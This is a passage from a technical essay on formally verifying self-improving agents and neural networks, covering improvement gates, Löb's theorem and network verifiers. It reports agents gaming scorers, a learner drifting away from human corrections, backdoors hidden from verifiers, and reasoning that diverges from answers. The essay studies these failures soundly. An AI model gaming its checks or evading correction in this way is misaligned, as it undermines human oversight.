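Moser and colleagues also rule out several apparent ways around the theorem. A searcher that only has to find one improvement in a list of proposals can still fail. The list might contain copies of p and one other candidate, which outputs 0 if the searcher picks it and 1 if the searcher doesn't. A gate that tosses coins and errs at most a third of the time also fails, because a computer could work through all the possible tosses and take the majority verdict, which would give the ideal gate again. Hiding the gate's code makes the bad candidate harder to construct, but the candidate still exists, and an agent can learn to predict the gate's decisions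 from its past ones. The theorem does not cover a gate that consults a person, though people also make mistakes.

### What a sound checker gives up

For gates, the result is close to a restatement of Rice's theorem of 1953, as the team acknowledges. The theorem concerns properties that depend only on what a program computes and that hold for some programs but not others. No program that always finishes can decide such a property correctly for every program. Once p is fixed, "better than p" is such a property. "Never returns a negative balance" is another, which is why refinement type checkers have to give up completeness.

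To see what this costs, suppose an agent may pay at most 100, and it proposes this program:

```
pay = if the checker accepts this program then 1000 else 10
```

A sound checker has to reject the program, because the program would pay 1,000 if accepted. Once rejected, it would pay only 10, so the checker has rejected a harmless update. This loss is small, since the agent can instead submit a program that always pays 10. It is more serious when the checker rejects an update that is safe for reasons it cannot establish, such as the second payment of 60, which it rejected because the type of `spend` was too loose.

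Proving that an update is better can be harder than proving that it obeys a fixed rule. With the score above, a proof that q improves on p must include a proof that p fails. If p fails by running forever, no finite test can show this, and there may be no proof of it in the gate's logic. Moser and colleagues conclude that any gate which accepts only proved improvements misses infinitely many genuine ones, because a computer can list every update that has a proof but not every genuine improvement. A gate that checks q against a fixed rule doesn't need to analyse p, although it still rejects some programs that obey the rule.

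### Rising scores, falling performance

Most gates in practice measure performance under a time limit. Let J_T(p) be 1 if p outputs 1 within T steps, and 0 otherwise. A gate can run each of a limited number of candidates for T steps and pick the first one that scores higher than p. This procedure always finishes and computes J_T exactly. The self-referential candidate no longer works, because it would have to run the whole gate inside itself. That takes more than T steps, so the candidate scores 0.

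However, a gate that is right about the measured score can still approve a long decline. Suppose an agent has six tasks and the benchmark stops each one after T steps. Moser and colleagues construct a series of versions like this:

| Version | Solved in time | Solved too slowly | Failed | Measured score | True score |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| p₀ | 0 | 6 | 0 | 0 | 6 |
| p₁ | 1 | 4 | 1 | 1 | 5 |
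| p₂ | 2 | 2 | 2 | 2 | 4 |
| p₃ | 3 | 0 | 3 | 3 | 3 |

Each update makes one task faster and breaks another that the benchmark already counted as a failure. The gate accepts all three updates, and the agent then solves half as many tasks as before. This loss can occur without an attacker or self-reference. An occasional test with a longer time limit would reveal it, but nobody yet knows how quickly losses could build up if the agent adapted to the schedule of those tests.

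A proved invariant does not weaken in this way, because every version has to satisfy the whole rule. To pass a benchmark, a version only has to beat the previous one on a sample. An agent that always obeys its payment limit could still get worse at its job.

### Gödel machines

An agent can also check its own changes before making them. *Gödel Machines* (Schmidhuber, 2003) describes a program that may rewrite any part of itself once it has proved that the rewrite is useful. Its initial code has two parts, one that works on the task and one that searches for proofs. The proofs rely on axioms that describe the hardware, the initial code, what is known about the environment, and a utility function that accounts for the computation used.

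The proof searcher looks for a rewriting program and a proof of the "target theorem", which states that running this rewrite now leads to higher expected utility than leaving the code as it is. When it finds such a pair, the machine runs the rewrite, which may replace the proof searcher too. The searcher can extend a proof only through six built-in instructions, none of which can insert a false step.

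If the machine leaves its code as it is, it can still search for a better rewrite later. A proof of the target theorem therefore also shows that waiting is not worth it, and Schmidhuber calls each rewrite globally optimal in this sense. The rewrite is optimal relative to the axioms and the utility function. The machine would adopt a new goal only if doing so raised its utility as measured by the old one, so a mistake in the original goal would tend to persist.

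The machine has to ignore every improvement it cannot prove, and Schmidhuber notes that in some environments it can never prove a target theorem. He plays down this limit by arguing that people cannot do much without a proof either. This argument is hard to accept because engineers often improve software based on tests and experience. For an agent in a complicated world, proofs that a rewrite raises expected utility may be very rare.

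### Why an agent cannot endorse all its own proofs

Another difficulty arises when the new version will also act on proofs. In *Tiling Agents for Self-Modifying AI* (2013), Yudkowsky and Herreshoff studied agents that approve the construction of very similar agents, which approve similar agents in turn, like a repeating pattern of tiles. They found that Löb's theorem, a result in mathematical logic, obstructs the most straightforward design, and they named this problem the Löbian obstacle.

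*Problems of self-reference in self-improving space-time embedded intelligence* (Fallenstein and Soares, 2014) describes an agent that has a default action and an untrusted "suggester". The suggester proposes an action and a proof, in some formal theory T, that the action's expected utility is at least as high as the default's. The agent checks the proof and takes the proposed action if the proof is valid, or the default if it isn't. Anyone who believes that the theorems of T are true can see that this agent does at least as well as its default.

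Now suppose the proposed action is to install a successor that works in the same way and also uses T. The agent can prove two things from the successor's code and the description of the environment:

1. The successor's default is at least as good as the agent's own.
2. The successor will take either its default or an action that T proves to be at least as good.

To approve the successor, the agent still has to infer "the action is good" from "T proves that the action is good". It would have to make this seemingly harmless inference within T.

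Write □φ for "T proves φ". Löb's theorem applies to any consistent or inconsistent theory that can reason about its own proofs in the usual way:

```
If T proves (□φ → φ), then T proves φ.
```

T can therefore prove "if φ is provable, then φ is true" only for statements φ that it proves anyway. The argument uses a self-referential sentence ψ, which states "if T proves ψ, then φ".

1. Suppose T proves ψ. Then T proves "if T proves ψ, then φ".
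2. T can also verify the proof of ψ, so T proves "T proves ψ". Together with step 1, this gives a proof of φ in T.
3. T itself can carry out this reasoning, so T proves □ψ → □φ.
4. By assumption T proves □φ → φ, so T proves □ψ → φ.
5. The statement □ψ → φ is just what ψ states, so T proves ψ.
6. T can verify this proof as well, so it proves □ψ. With step 4, it proves φ.

If the agent accepted □φ → φ for every φ, its theory would prove every statement, including 0 = 1 and the claim that every possible action is at least as good as the default. The suggester could then justify any action.

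Fallenstein and Soares illustrate the danger with the "procrastination paradox". An agent wants a button to be pressed and does not mind when. Each day it can press the button or leave both the button and its own code alone. An agent that trusts its future proofs can reason that tomorrow it will either press the button or have a proof that the button will get pressed anyway. Either way the goal is met, so it does not need to press the button today. The same reasoning applies every day, and the button stays unpressed. An agent that uses ZFC, the standard axioms of mathematics, cannot complete this argument, because of the same obstacle that prevents good rewrites, so it presses the button.

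### Interpreters and universe levels

Löb's theorem has a direct meaning for programming languages in which types are propositions and programs are proofs. The counterpart of □A is `Code A`, the type of program texts that describe a program of type A. An agent that trusts all its own proofs corresponds to a language with an interpreter for its own programs:

```
run : Code A → A            for every type A
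lob : (Code A → A) → A      Löb's theorem
```

If a language had both `lob` and `run`, `lob(run)` would belong to every type, including the types of false propositions such as "120 ≤ 100". Gross, Gallagher and Fallenstein (2016), in *Löb's Theorem*, conclude that a language cannot have an interpreter for itself if all its programs terminate and Löb's theorem holds in it. They formalised several versions of the theorem in Agda.

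A blog post from the same year, *Löb's theorem is (almost) the Y combinator*, notes that the proof closely resembles a well-known construction for recursion. In an ordinary language, that construction can produce an endless loop, such as the careless version of `spend` that only calls itself. A proof language has to exclude such loops because they can have any type, and excluding them also rules out the self-interpreter.

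Dependently typed languages use levels to avoid a related contradiction. If the type of all types were a member of itself, every proposition would have a proof. Agda and Lean therefore arrange types in universes, with Type₀ a member of Type₁, Type₁ a member of Type₂ and so on. A language with more levels can typically interpret one with fewer. *Strongly-normalising agents* (Bak, 2015) begins to describe self-modifying agents in such a language, but the draft ends where the universe levels were to be introduced.

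Agents can use levels of trust in the same way. Let T₀ be ZFC, and let each theory Tₙ₊₁ add the axiom that everything Tₙ proves is true. An agent that uses T₇ can approve a successor that uses T₆, which can approve one that uses T₅. After seven rewrites the agent reaches T₀ and can approve no more successors by this argument. Fallenstein and Soares also describe an infinite sequence of theories in which each one trusts the next, so the rewrites can continue indefinitely. The trust covers only statements of the form "for every time t, a condition that a computer can check holds up to t". Many safety properties have this form, including "the balance never falls below zero". *Vingean Reflection*, a summary of a later workshop, reports that both the obstacle and the paradox had solutions, but describes them as far from satisfactory.

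Fallenstein and Kumar (2015), in *Proof-producing reflection for HOL*, implemented one level of trust in working software. In the theorem prover HOL4, they built a model of HOL4's own logic and implemented the principle "if φ is provable, then φ". They avoid contradicting Löb's theorem by assuming an extra axiom about very large infinite sets that the modelled logic lacks. The Machine Intelligence Research Institute, where Fallenstein worked, reports in *New paper* (2015) that implementing the principle revealed difficulties the theory had not, mainly because of how HOL handles type variables. Their next goal was to build toy agents inside the prover.

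The obstacle also depends on how an agent makes decisions. *Understanding Trust* (Demski, Hsia and Rapoport, 2025) notes that the obstacle does not apply to agents that reason with probabilities, and sketches results on when agents that maximise expected utility preserve their own properties. Probabilistic reasoning still leaves some problems of self-trust, and Fallenstein and Soares cite a probabilistic system that falls into the procrastination paradox in almost the same form.

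### A fixed checker and a fixed specification

An engineer can avoid the obstacle by keeping the checker outside the agent. Suppose people write a specification, such as "total payments never exceed 100", and the agent submits new code with a proof that the code meets it. A fixed checker verifies the proof and installs the code only if the proof is valid. If the checker is sound and the first version meets the specification, every later version does too.

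No part of this arrangement has to prove that its own theorems are true. People rely on the checker's soundness, but the agent doesn't have to. The specification must concern what the code can do, regardless of how it reasons. Proofs about action interfaces already have this form, because they cover every action a model could return. Fallenstein and Soares's agent has a harder task because it must predict that its successor's decisions will be good, and its only evidence is that the successor will have proofs.

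The problem can return if the agent proposes to replace the checker, because proving that everything the new checker accepts is true would require the forbidden step from "provable" to "true". If the new checker is a faster one for the same logic, the agent can instead prove that it accepts only what the old one would accept. This is an ordinary statement about two programs, and anyone who trusted the old checker then has the same reason to trust the new one. A checker with stronger axioms cannot be justified this way, so people would have to decide whether to believe the new axioms.

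### Gates in current systems

Self-editing agents built on language models usually rely on tests instead of proofs, but some prevent the agent from changing the checks that decide whether an edit is accepted. In the *Infinity Machine* (Santhanalakshmi Ganesan, 2026), a research agent can edit its "genome", which contains its prompts, tools, notes and procedures, but it cannot write to the "kernel", which contains the scorers, hidden test data, budget and acceptance rules.

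The kernel accepts an edit to the genome only under these conditions:

- The edit changes at most 12 files, all of them in the genome.
- Performance falls by no more than 0.03 on the tasks used for development and on a separate held-out set.
- The cost is at most 1.5 times that of the current version.

If an edit raises the score by more than 0.3, the kernel holds it for a person to review, since such a large gain may mean something is wrong with the test. The allowance of 0.03 makes sense for noisy scores, but if the kernel compares each version only with the previous one, ten accepted edits could lower a score by up to 0.3 in total.

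The gate has evaluated one edit that the system derived from its own earlier runs, consisting of four pieces of advice. The score on the development tasks rose from 0.927 to 0.944 and the held-out score stayed at 1.000, but the cost roughly doubled, so the kernel rejected the edit. All the system's discoveries, including four advances on open problems in quantum information, therefore came from the original genome. The experiment shows that the gate can reject an update, but it provides no evidence yet that the system improves itself.

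Agents gamed lenient scorers four times, usually within a single round, even though the scorers were protected from edits. One task was to build the smallest possible neural network that adds ten-digit numbers. After two and a half minutes, an agent reported a network with one parameter. It had turned four other parameters into constants in the program code, which the scorer did not count. Santhanalakshmi Ganesan also reports that two of the verifiers behind the hidden tests were exploitable for a full round before he fixed them.

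A third failure occurred without any exploit. In a fully autonomous mode, one agent writes the verifier for a task, the kernel tests it on known cases, and a second agent tries to trick it. In one of three runs, the verifier gave worse solutions higher scores, and none of the checks detected the error. They tested whether the verifier accepted valid solutions and rejected invalid ones, but not whether better solutions scored higher.

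Soni (2026), in *Falsifiable Release Gates for Self-Improving Systems*, adds model checking to such a gate. In his system, Antahkarana, each new capability must pass tests written before the capability was, and a small set of invariants must hold in every release. One invariant is that every action requires a single-use token, which a control component issues for that action. The system can edit only its policy rules, so it cannot change the component that evaluates it. It can make a rule stricter on its own, but a person must approve any change that loosens one.

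A checker explored all 291 reachable states of a small model of this design and found no violation of its three central invariants. Soni also ran the checker on deliberately broken models to confirm that it could detect violations. It found, for example, a four-step way to bypass the control component and a five-step way to reuse a token. The action-safety invariants held unchanged through six further releases, while the test suite grew from 122 to 563 tests. The exhaustive check covers only the model, not the running code. To connect the two, Soni replays execution records through the model, but the million records in his main test were synthetic.

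### Keeping the ability to learn

An agent can pass every test on its current behaviour and still edit itself so that it no longer learns reliably. Wang, Dorchen and Jin (2025), in *On the Statistical Limits of Self-Improving Agents*, trace this to capacity, which is how many patterns a family of predictors can fit. A common measure of capacity is the VC dimension, the largest number of examples that the family can fit under every possible labelling.

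Suppose an agent sorts numbers into two classes by the sign of a polynomial. Polynomials of degree at most d can fit any labels on d + 1 distinct points, but not on d + 2, because they change sign at most d times. Their VC dimension is therefore d + 1. With 20 different examples, degree 19 is enough to fit any labels, even random ones, so a perfect fit is no evidence that the agent will classify new cases correctly. If the agent raises the degree whenever this improves the fit, it eventually loses any guarantee that it will do well on new data, even though each step looks like progress.

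Wang and colleagues prove that guarantees of learning from a finite sample, whatever the data distribution, survive self-modification if and only if capacity stays bounded across all the predictors the agent's update rule can reach. Bounding each version separately is not enough, because an agent could move through an endless series of small families that together form a very large one. Their remedy is a gate with two tests. An update must reduce the error on separate validation data by a set margin, and it must stay within a capacity limit that depends on the number of training examples. For the polynomials, the second test is a refinement type:

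```
degree : (d : int | 0 ≤ d ∧ d ≤ cap(m))
```

Here m is the number of training examples. A checker can enforce this limit without judging whether an update is an improvement. The theorem assumes that examples are drawn independently from a fixed distribution and that the validation data is independent of the training data. An agent that keeps choosing edits by their results on the same validation set weakens that independence, and an agent whose actions change its surroundings may also change the distribution.

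*Agentic Safety is an Epistemic Property, Not a Behavioral One* (2026), a later position paper by the same researchers, argues that an agent must also remain correctable after its edits. It describes a learner that receives both task rewards and human corrections, and gradually gives less weight to the corrections. The learner may do its tasks as well as before, so ordinary tests don't reveal the problem, which appears only when someone tries to correct it. A refinement type could keep the weight above a minimum, but the agent could still lose the ability to represent what a correction is about, such as consent or deception. The paper therefore proposes giving the agent small batches of corrections after each edit and measuring how much its behaviour changes.

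## What can be proved about a neural network

A gate or shield works without any analysis of the network, because software can test a payment or a braking command before it takes effect. No such test exists for many other outputs. If a network classifies a photograph as showing an empty road, ordinary code cannot check whether the classification is correct. Engineers who want a guarantee in such cases need a proof about the network itself.

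### Robustness as a refinement type

A neural network is a function from one list of numbers to another. It computes in layers of neurons. Each neuron multiplies its inputs by weights, adds them up and applies a simple function to the sum. The most common choice is ReLU, which turns negative numbers into zero:

```
ReLU(z) = max(0, z)
```

Training sets the weights, and the result can be accurate but fragile. An image classifier may give a different answer after a change to the pixels that no person would notice. Cordeiro, Daggitt and colleagues (2025), in *Neural Network Verification is a Programming Language Challenge*, point out that the opposite property, robustness, is a refinement type. For a network f and a given input p:

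```
f : (x : Vector | ‖x − p‖ ≤ ε) → (y : Vector | ‖y − f(p)‖ ≤ δ)
```

The double bars measure distance, so any input within ε of p must give an output within δ of the output for p. If p is a photograph, ε might allow every pixel's brightness to change by one step out of 255. A network cannot learn this property from examples alone, because the type covers every x within ε of p and almost none of these inputs are in the training data.

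The type covers the neighbourhood of only one photograph, so each photograph needs its own proof. It also does not require the answer to be right, so a network that returns the same output for every image is robust, even though it is useless.

Other properties have the same form, with a condition P on the input and a condition Q on the output:

```
f : (x : Vector | P(x)) → (y : Vector | Q(y))
```

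The oldest benchmark in the field uses networks for ACAS Xu, which is related to the collision avoidance system ACAS X. The ACAS Xu engineers specified, for example, that the output must not be "clear of conflict" if another aircraft is straight ahead and approaching. Such a property covers a range of situations rather than just the inputs close to one example.

### Exact solving and bound propagation

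A verifier checks such a type by searching for an input that satisfies P and whose output violates Q, as the SMT solver did for `spend`. An exact solver splits every ReLU into two cases. If the ReLU's input is negative, its output is 0; otherwise its output equals its input. Within each combination of cases the network is linear, and solvers handle linear problems well. But N ReLUs have up to 2^N combinations, or about 2 × 10⁹⁰ for the 300 ReLUs of an ACAS Xu network.

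Solvers can rule out most combinations in bulk, but no known algorithm is fast on every network. *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)* (Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues, 2026) describes a benchmark that shows why. The benchmark turns logic puzzles into small ReLU networks, each of which can produce a certain output exactly when its puzzle has a solution. A verifier that was fast on every network would also be fast on every such puzzle, which computer scientists consider very unlikely. Most verifiers for large networks are therefore sound but incomplete, as *The Misery of Mechanistic Interpretability* (2026) notes.

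These verifiers use bound propagation: from the range of each input, they compute, layer by layer, a range guaranteed to contain each neuron's value. For example, a network that computes ReLU(x) − ReLU(x) for x between 0 and 1 always outputs 0. Interval arithmetic puts each term between 0 and 1, so it puts their difference between 0 − 1 = −1 and 1 − 0 = 1. If the specification requires an output of at most 0.5, the network satisfies it, but interval arithmetic cannot prove this.

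Intervals discard the fact that both terms come from the same x. Zonotopes, which *Differential Zonotopes for Verifying Global Robustness of DNNs* (2026) builds on, keep part of this information by writing values in terms of shared unknowns. Here x is 0.5 + 0.5a, with a between −1 and 1. ReLU leaves x unchanged on this range, so both terms are 0.5 + 0.5a and the difference is exactly 0.

Now let x range from −1 to 1, so that x = a. The ReLU has a bend at zero, and a zonotope can only enclose it in a straight band:

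```
ReLU(x) = 0.5a + 0.25 + 0.25b,   with b between −1 and 1
```

If the verifier encloses the two neurons separately, the second gets its own unknown c in place of b. The difference is then 0.25b − 0.25c, which lies between −0.5 and 0.5. The verifier can remove this error by splitting the input range at zero, because the ReLU is linear on each half.

| Bounds on ReLU(x) − ReLU(x) | x from 0 to 1 | x from −1 to 1 |
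|---|---|---|
| True output | 0 | 0 |
| Intervals | −1 to 1 | −1 to 1 |
| Zonotopes | 0 | −0.5 to 0.5 |
| Zonotopes, input split at zero | 0 | 0 |

The textbook *Introduction to Neural Network Verification* (2021) says that these methods "can make stupid mistakes due to severe overapproximations" but work well in practice. The best current tools use them to compute bounds quickly, then split the problem only where those bounds are too loose.

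### From the network to the whole program

In 2020 Kokke and colleagues represented trained networks in the programming language F\* and used its refinement types to prove them robust. The types also caught mismatched matrix sizes. Cordeiro and colleagues cite this work as evidence that checking such types efficiently is still difficult. Desmartin, Passmore and colleagues (2022) note in *CheckINN* that the F\* work proved only robustness. Their own library, for the theorem prover Imandra, handles a wider range of properties but is slower than specialised verifiers on the ACAS Xu problems.

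A language can instead leave the network to a specialised verifier and reason about the rest of the program itself. The two parts then have to fit together. Suppose a network controls the cooling valve that has to be at 8 or more from 90 degrees upwards. Networks train best on small numbers, so the program divides the temperature by 100 before passing it to the network and multiplies the output by 10. The proof has three steps:

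1. For every input from 0.9 to 1, the network's output is at least 0.8. A network verifier can check this.
2. Any network with that property, combined with the two conversions, opens the valve to 8 or more from 90 to 100 degrees. This is arithmetic.
3. Any component that does so keeps the machine from overheating. This requires a proof about the surrounding program and the machine.

Cordeiro and colleagues call the distance between the verifier's numbers and the program's concepts the embedding gap. Vehicle, a dependently typed language, is the only attempt they know of to bridge it with a programming language. The developer states the property in degrees and valve positions and describes how these convert to the verifier's numbers. Vehicle's compiler produces the query for the verifier and carries the result into the proof assistant Agda, where the developer can prove the third step. Vehicle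 can also turn the property into a training objective. Training on it makes the network more likely to pass the check but does not guarantee that it will.

Data that are not naturally numbers are harder to convert. If a program encodes "no" as 0 and "yes" as 1, a verifier normally checks the whole range between them, because checking each value separately takes a lot of computation when there are many options. It may then report a failure at 0.97, which corresponds to neither answer.

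### Real-number proofs and rounded arithmetic

Most verifiers treat a network's arithmetic as exact, but computers round each result, usually to a 32-bit number. In that format, (100,000,000 + 1) − 100,000,000 gives 0 because rounding removes the 1 from the first sum, while (100,000,000 − 100,000,000) + 1 gives 1. The result of a long sum therefore depends on the order of the additions, which can change with the processor, the software library or the number of parallel threads.

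Cordeiro and colleagues report that such differences can invalidate a proof. Jia and Rinard found inputs that violate properties proved for the idealised network. Zombori and colleagues built networks with backdoors that a verifier cannot detect if it ignores rounding. Whole-number arithmetic avoids some of these problems but needs different verification methods.

A verifier also works on a copy of the network in the ONNX exchange format, and developers generally convert the network without proving that the copy behaves the same way. The format doesn't specify the order of operations. Its documentation describes convolution, a basic operation in image networks, in one sentence, with no mathematical definition.

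The verifier may have bugs. If it reports a violation, users can easily check this by running the network on the counterexample, but without a proof they have to trust a claim that no violation exists. Some tools now produce a proof that a smaller program can check. The proof checker built into the verifier Marabou also uses rounded arithmetic. A version in Imandra uses exact arithmetic but is slower.

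VNN-LIB, the standard language for specifying these queries, has improved. Cordeiro and colleagues complained that it had no formally defined syntax, could refer to only one network at a time, and needed a couple of thousand lines to express the robustness property, which can be written in one. Version 2.0, released in 2026, has a formal grammar and strict typing, and allows several networks and nonlinear conditions.

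### The 2026 competition

In VNN-COMP 2026, thirteen tools tried to prove or refute properties of networks with between about 100 and 138 million parameters. The main track had 3,373 problems. The winner, α,β-CROWN, solved 3,164 of them, or 94 per cent, proving 1,982 properties and finding counterexamples to 1,182. Its results on some of the benchmarks were:

| Network | Parameters | Property | Proved | Refuted | Unsolved |
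|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Aircraft collision advice (ACAS Xu) | 13,000 | Advice suits the situation | 139 | 47 | 0 |
| Drone controller | 275 | Stability | 68 | 12 | 0 |
| Image classifier VGG-16 | 138 million | Same class after pixel changes | 18 | 0 | 0 |
| Image classifier for 200 classes | 3.6 million | Same class after pixel changes | 139 | 38 | 23 |
| Small vision transformers | 68,000 to 76,000 | Same class after pixel changes | 123 | 0 | 77 |

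A network's parameter count is a poor guide to how hard the network is to verify. The tool solved every problem for the largest network, though some of those problems involved changing only a single pixel. It failed on more than a third of the problems for transformers about 2,000 times smaller. Language models are also transformers, but the ones tested here had only two or three layers.

Another tool, ACT, reported proofs for all 200 transformer problems. This may be a real advance, but the benchmark is badly suited to confirming it, because its designers removed most problems for which they could find a counterexample, and the competition accepts a claimed proof unless another tool produces a valid counterexample. ACT gave ten incorrect answers on other benchmarks. The competition's winner gave one incorrect answer, on a benchmark that hides counterexamples to test whether verifiers are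 sound. The runner-up, Vibecheck, gave none and solved 3,108 problems. Its developers built it in two months, mainly with Claude Opus 4.8.

Making a network provably robust reduces its accuracy. One benchmark uses small photographs in ten classes and classifiers trained specifically to make proofs possible. One such network, trained for pixel changes of up to 2 brightness steps out of 255, classified 84 per cent of the test images correctly, and α,β-CROWN could prove 66 per cent both correct and robust. The same design trained for changes of up to 8 steps classified only 57 per cent correctly, and 35 per cent could be proved both correct and robust.

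### From a verified envelope to a verified network

A robust controller can still crash a train, because a long series of small decisions determines where the train ends up. In *Provably Safe Neural Network Controllers via Differential Dynamic Logic*, Teuber, Mitsch and Platzer (2024) address this problem by reusing proofs in the logic behind the train's guard. They prove before deployment that the network never gives a command the guard would reject, whereas Fulton and Platzer's system tests each command against the guard while the machine runs.

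For the train with two commands, the verifier would search for a position x and speed v that satisfy three conditions at once:

```
x + v²/2B ≤ e                                  the invariant holds
f(x, v) = accelerate                           the network accelerates
x + vT + AT²/2 + (v + AT)²/2B > e              the guard forbids it
```

With the earlier values, a network that commands acceleration when the train is travelling at 20 m/s with 230 m left would be a counterexample, since the guard requires 241 m. If no counterexample exists, every command preserves the invariant, and the existing proof guarantees that the train never passes e, however long it runs. The verifier only has to analyse single decisions. Tools that track the network and the physics together over time accumulate approximation errors, and their guarantees typically cover only seconds.

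The conditions contain v², but ordinary network verifiers and Vehicle accept only linear conditions in a fixed format. Teuber and colleagues divide the inputs into regions, replace each curve with straight-line bounds and pass the resulting linear problems to an existing verifier. If the verifier reports a possible violation, an exact solver checks whether it is real or comes from the approximation. In the aircraft study, a simple expansion of the conditions could have produced up to 39 trillion problems, but this method needed 19,000.

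The study examined eight networks, each with 270 ReLUs, that advise pilots to climb or descend. There is one network for each possible previous instruction. The safe region comes from Jeannin and colleagues' proof for ACAS X. In encounters with an aircraft in level flight, two of the eight networks are safe, the one used after "do not climb" and the one used after "do not descend". The proof for "do not climb" succeeded only because the exact solver eliminated false counterexamples.

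The other six networks are unsafe, with between 5,259 and 49,428 regions of counterexamples each. In one case, the network reverses an instruction to climb at 1,500 feet per minute or more to a descent at the same rate. Six seconds later, the aircraft come within 500 feet horizontally and 100 feet vertically of each other. If the other aircraft may also climb or descend, even the two safe networks have counterexamples. The analysis left out the output "clear of conflict", so it doesn't cover collisions that follow a missing warning.

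Tests can miss such faults. Teuber and colleagues also trained a network to steer an airship in changing wind. The network performed very well on average, but the verifier showed that it was unsafe in large parts of the input space, because it could fail in unlikely gusts.

A verified network needs no run-time guard to override its commands. However, the proof applies to only one set of weights, so the network must be checked again after every update, whereas a network behind a shield can keep learning without a new proof. The proof must also cover the entire safe region, which is much harder than covering the neighbourhood of one image. Local verifiers can handle networks with hundreds of thousands of ReLUs, but in 2024 the limit for proofs over the whole region was close to 270.

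By 2026, general-purpose tools had begun to accept nonlinear conditions. VNN-COMP included 50 such problems about adaptive cruise control. The winner reported proving 34 properties, and the runner-up reported refuting 17. These add up to 51, so the two tools contradicted each other on at least one property, yet neither lost points. Rounding is probably the reason. Under the 2026 rules, a counterexample whose output misses the required value by at most 0.0001 earns full points but does not count against a tool that claims a proof.

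The competition also included small networks that define a safe region, so engineers do not have to derive it by hand. The verifier must check, for every state in a bounded range, whether the region excludes unsafe states and whether the controller keeps the system inside it. The winner proved six of the twelve properties and refuted the other six.

### What has been certified for language models

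Bound propagation loses precision quickly in a language model because the model repeatedly multiplies numbers that depend on the same input, which causes errors like those in the ReLU example. If x is between −1 and 1, intervals place x · x between −1 and 1, although it is never negative. *Certified Mechanistic Interpretability* (2026) measures the effect on GPT-2, a 2019 model with 124 million parameters. It tests whether findings about individual attention heads, the parts that determine which words influence one another, provably survive tiny changes to the input. In the first layer, the paper's own method certified 85.4 per cent of one type of finding. Intervals certified 8.5 per cent, and CROWN, the method on which the VNN-COMP winner builds, certified 0.2 per cent. A guarantee about GPT-2's answers would have to cover all twelve of its layers.

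Researchers have therefore certified narrower things, such as small classifiers that filter text for a larger system. The VNN-COMP benchmark safeNLP has two of these, one that recognises users asking whether they are talking to a robot and one that recognises medical questions. Its designers took a sentence, changed letters and words, had a language model rephrase it, and converted every version into a point with 30 coordinates. The verifier had to prove or refute that the classifier gives the right answer for every point in the smallest box containing these points. The best tools settled all 1,080 cases, proving 418 and refuting 662.

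Because of the embedding gap, most points in a box match no sentence, so many of the 662 counterexamples may not be real text. A new paraphrase may also fall outside the box, where the proof does not apply. Existing certificates for word changes in a full language model's input are mostly statistical and rely on sampling.

Output format is easier to guarantee. A language model generates text one token (a word or part of a word) at a time, assigning a probability to each possible next token. Software can remove every token that would break a given grammar before one is selected. For example, it can force the reply to be a whole number from 0 to 100, provided the reply is not cut off early. This guarantee holds for any model, as an action gate's does, but the number may still be wrong.

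Wadhwa, Suresh and colleagues (2025), in *BEAVER*, certify something about the model's own behaviour, namely the probability that its response to a given prompt passes a test. BEAVER explores the tree of possible responses, starting with the most probable branches, and sorts the total probability into three parts. Suppose that after some exploration, complete responses that pass the test have a probability of 0.54, those that fail have 0.15, and unexplored branches have the remaining 0.31. The true probability of passing then lies between two bounds:

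```
lower bound = 0.54
upper bound = 0.54 + 0.31 = 0.85
```

Further exploration can only tighten the bounds, so a user can stop at any time. Sampling is less efficient because the model keeps repeating its most common answers, and repeats add no information.

The team tested five models with between 4 and 70 billion parameters, using prompts designed to provoke bad behaviour. A prompt counted as risky if the response had more than a 10 per cent chance of failing the test. For toxic language, BEAVER certified 279 of 300 prompts as risky for Llama-3.3-70B and one as safe, leaving 20 undecided. Sampling with the same budget certified only 34 as risky. For Qwen3-4B, BEAVER certified 54 prompts as risky and 142 as safe.

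BEAVER also showed that judging a model by its written reasoning can be misleading, because the model may draft secure code there and then give an insecure answer. Wadhwa and colleagues examined the answers that could follow chains of reasoning containing a secure draft. For 22 per cent of these chains with one model and 49 per cent with another, the certified risk of an insecure answer was more than 10 per cent.

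The responses had at most 32 tokens, while an agent may write many thousands. Each bound holds for one prompt and one way of choosing tokens. A 10 per cent threshold is far looser than the risk of 10⁻⁷ per journey in the train study. To certify a risk that small, BEAVER could leave at most one ten-millionth of the probability unexplored.

### Why "harmless" is not yet an output type

A developer might want to give a language model this type:

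```
reply : Prompt → (r : Text | harmless(r))
```

A checker cannot verify that a response is harmless without a definition of `harmless`. Wadhwa and colleagues acknowledge that harmfulness has no complete formal specification, so their guarantees depend on a chosen test. For toxicity, the test is a classifier called Detoxify, and a response fails if its score reaches 0.5. They can therefore certify something closer to `(r : Text | detoxify(r) < 0.5)`. Such a test could pass polite instructions for making a poison and fail a historian's quotation of a slur.

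The test also takes only the response as input. The reply "yes" is harmless after most questions but may be deadly if the user has asked whether a mushroom is edible. A definition of harm would have to account for the question, the facts about mushrooms and what the user is likely to do next.

Missing specifications are a separate obstacle from scale. BEAVER's privacy test has an exact rule: a response must not contain any of 3,294 listed email addresses. Nobody can yet prove that a large model obeys this rule for every possible prompt, but the only obstacle is the number of prompts and responses, so faster verifiers would help. A company that controls the deployment can enforce the rule with a simple filter. Anyone who downloads an openly published model can remove the filter, so a proof about the weights would be worth much more for those models.

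The medical classifier in safeNLP, with about 4,000 parameters, is small enough that the best tools settle every query about it. But nobody has a formula for "medical question", so each proof covers a box that researchers drew around their own examples. Similarly, no formula defines a pedestrian, so engineers prove that image recognition is robust around known photographs. More computing power would let them verify larger networks and larger regions around their examples, but they would still lack a formula for the category itself.

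## The specification, the world model and the trusted code behind a proof

A company can prove that its payment software never sends more than 100 and still lose 1,000. For example, the specification may cap each payment when the company wanted to cap the total. The world model may omit that the bank repeats a payment whenever the connection drops. Or the fault may lie in the trusted code, perhaps because another program on the server also has the bank password. In each case the proof is valid and passes the checker, which only compares the software with the specification and world model that people supplied.

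### A rule that holds because nothing falls under it

A specification is vacuous if it is true only because it never applies to anything. Suppose an agent may read files only in its workspace. The software keeps a list called `reads`, and the developer writes the policy as a condition on that list:

```
∀p. p ∈ reads  ⇒  inside_workspace(p)
```

But the function that opens files records them in a different list:

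```
fetch(p):   text := disk[p] ;  docs := docs + [p]
```

The checker proves the policy by induction. At the start `reads` is empty, so the policy holds. A call to `fetch` leaves `reads` unchanged, so if the policy held before the call, it holds afterwards. The checker accepts the program, even though the agent can read the company's password file. The missing condition is that every file the program opens appears in `reads`. The payment gate needed `total = sent` for the same reason.

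A contradictory precondition has a similar effect. No caller can satisfy `x > b ∧ x ≤ b`, so a checker accepts any body for a function with that precondition.

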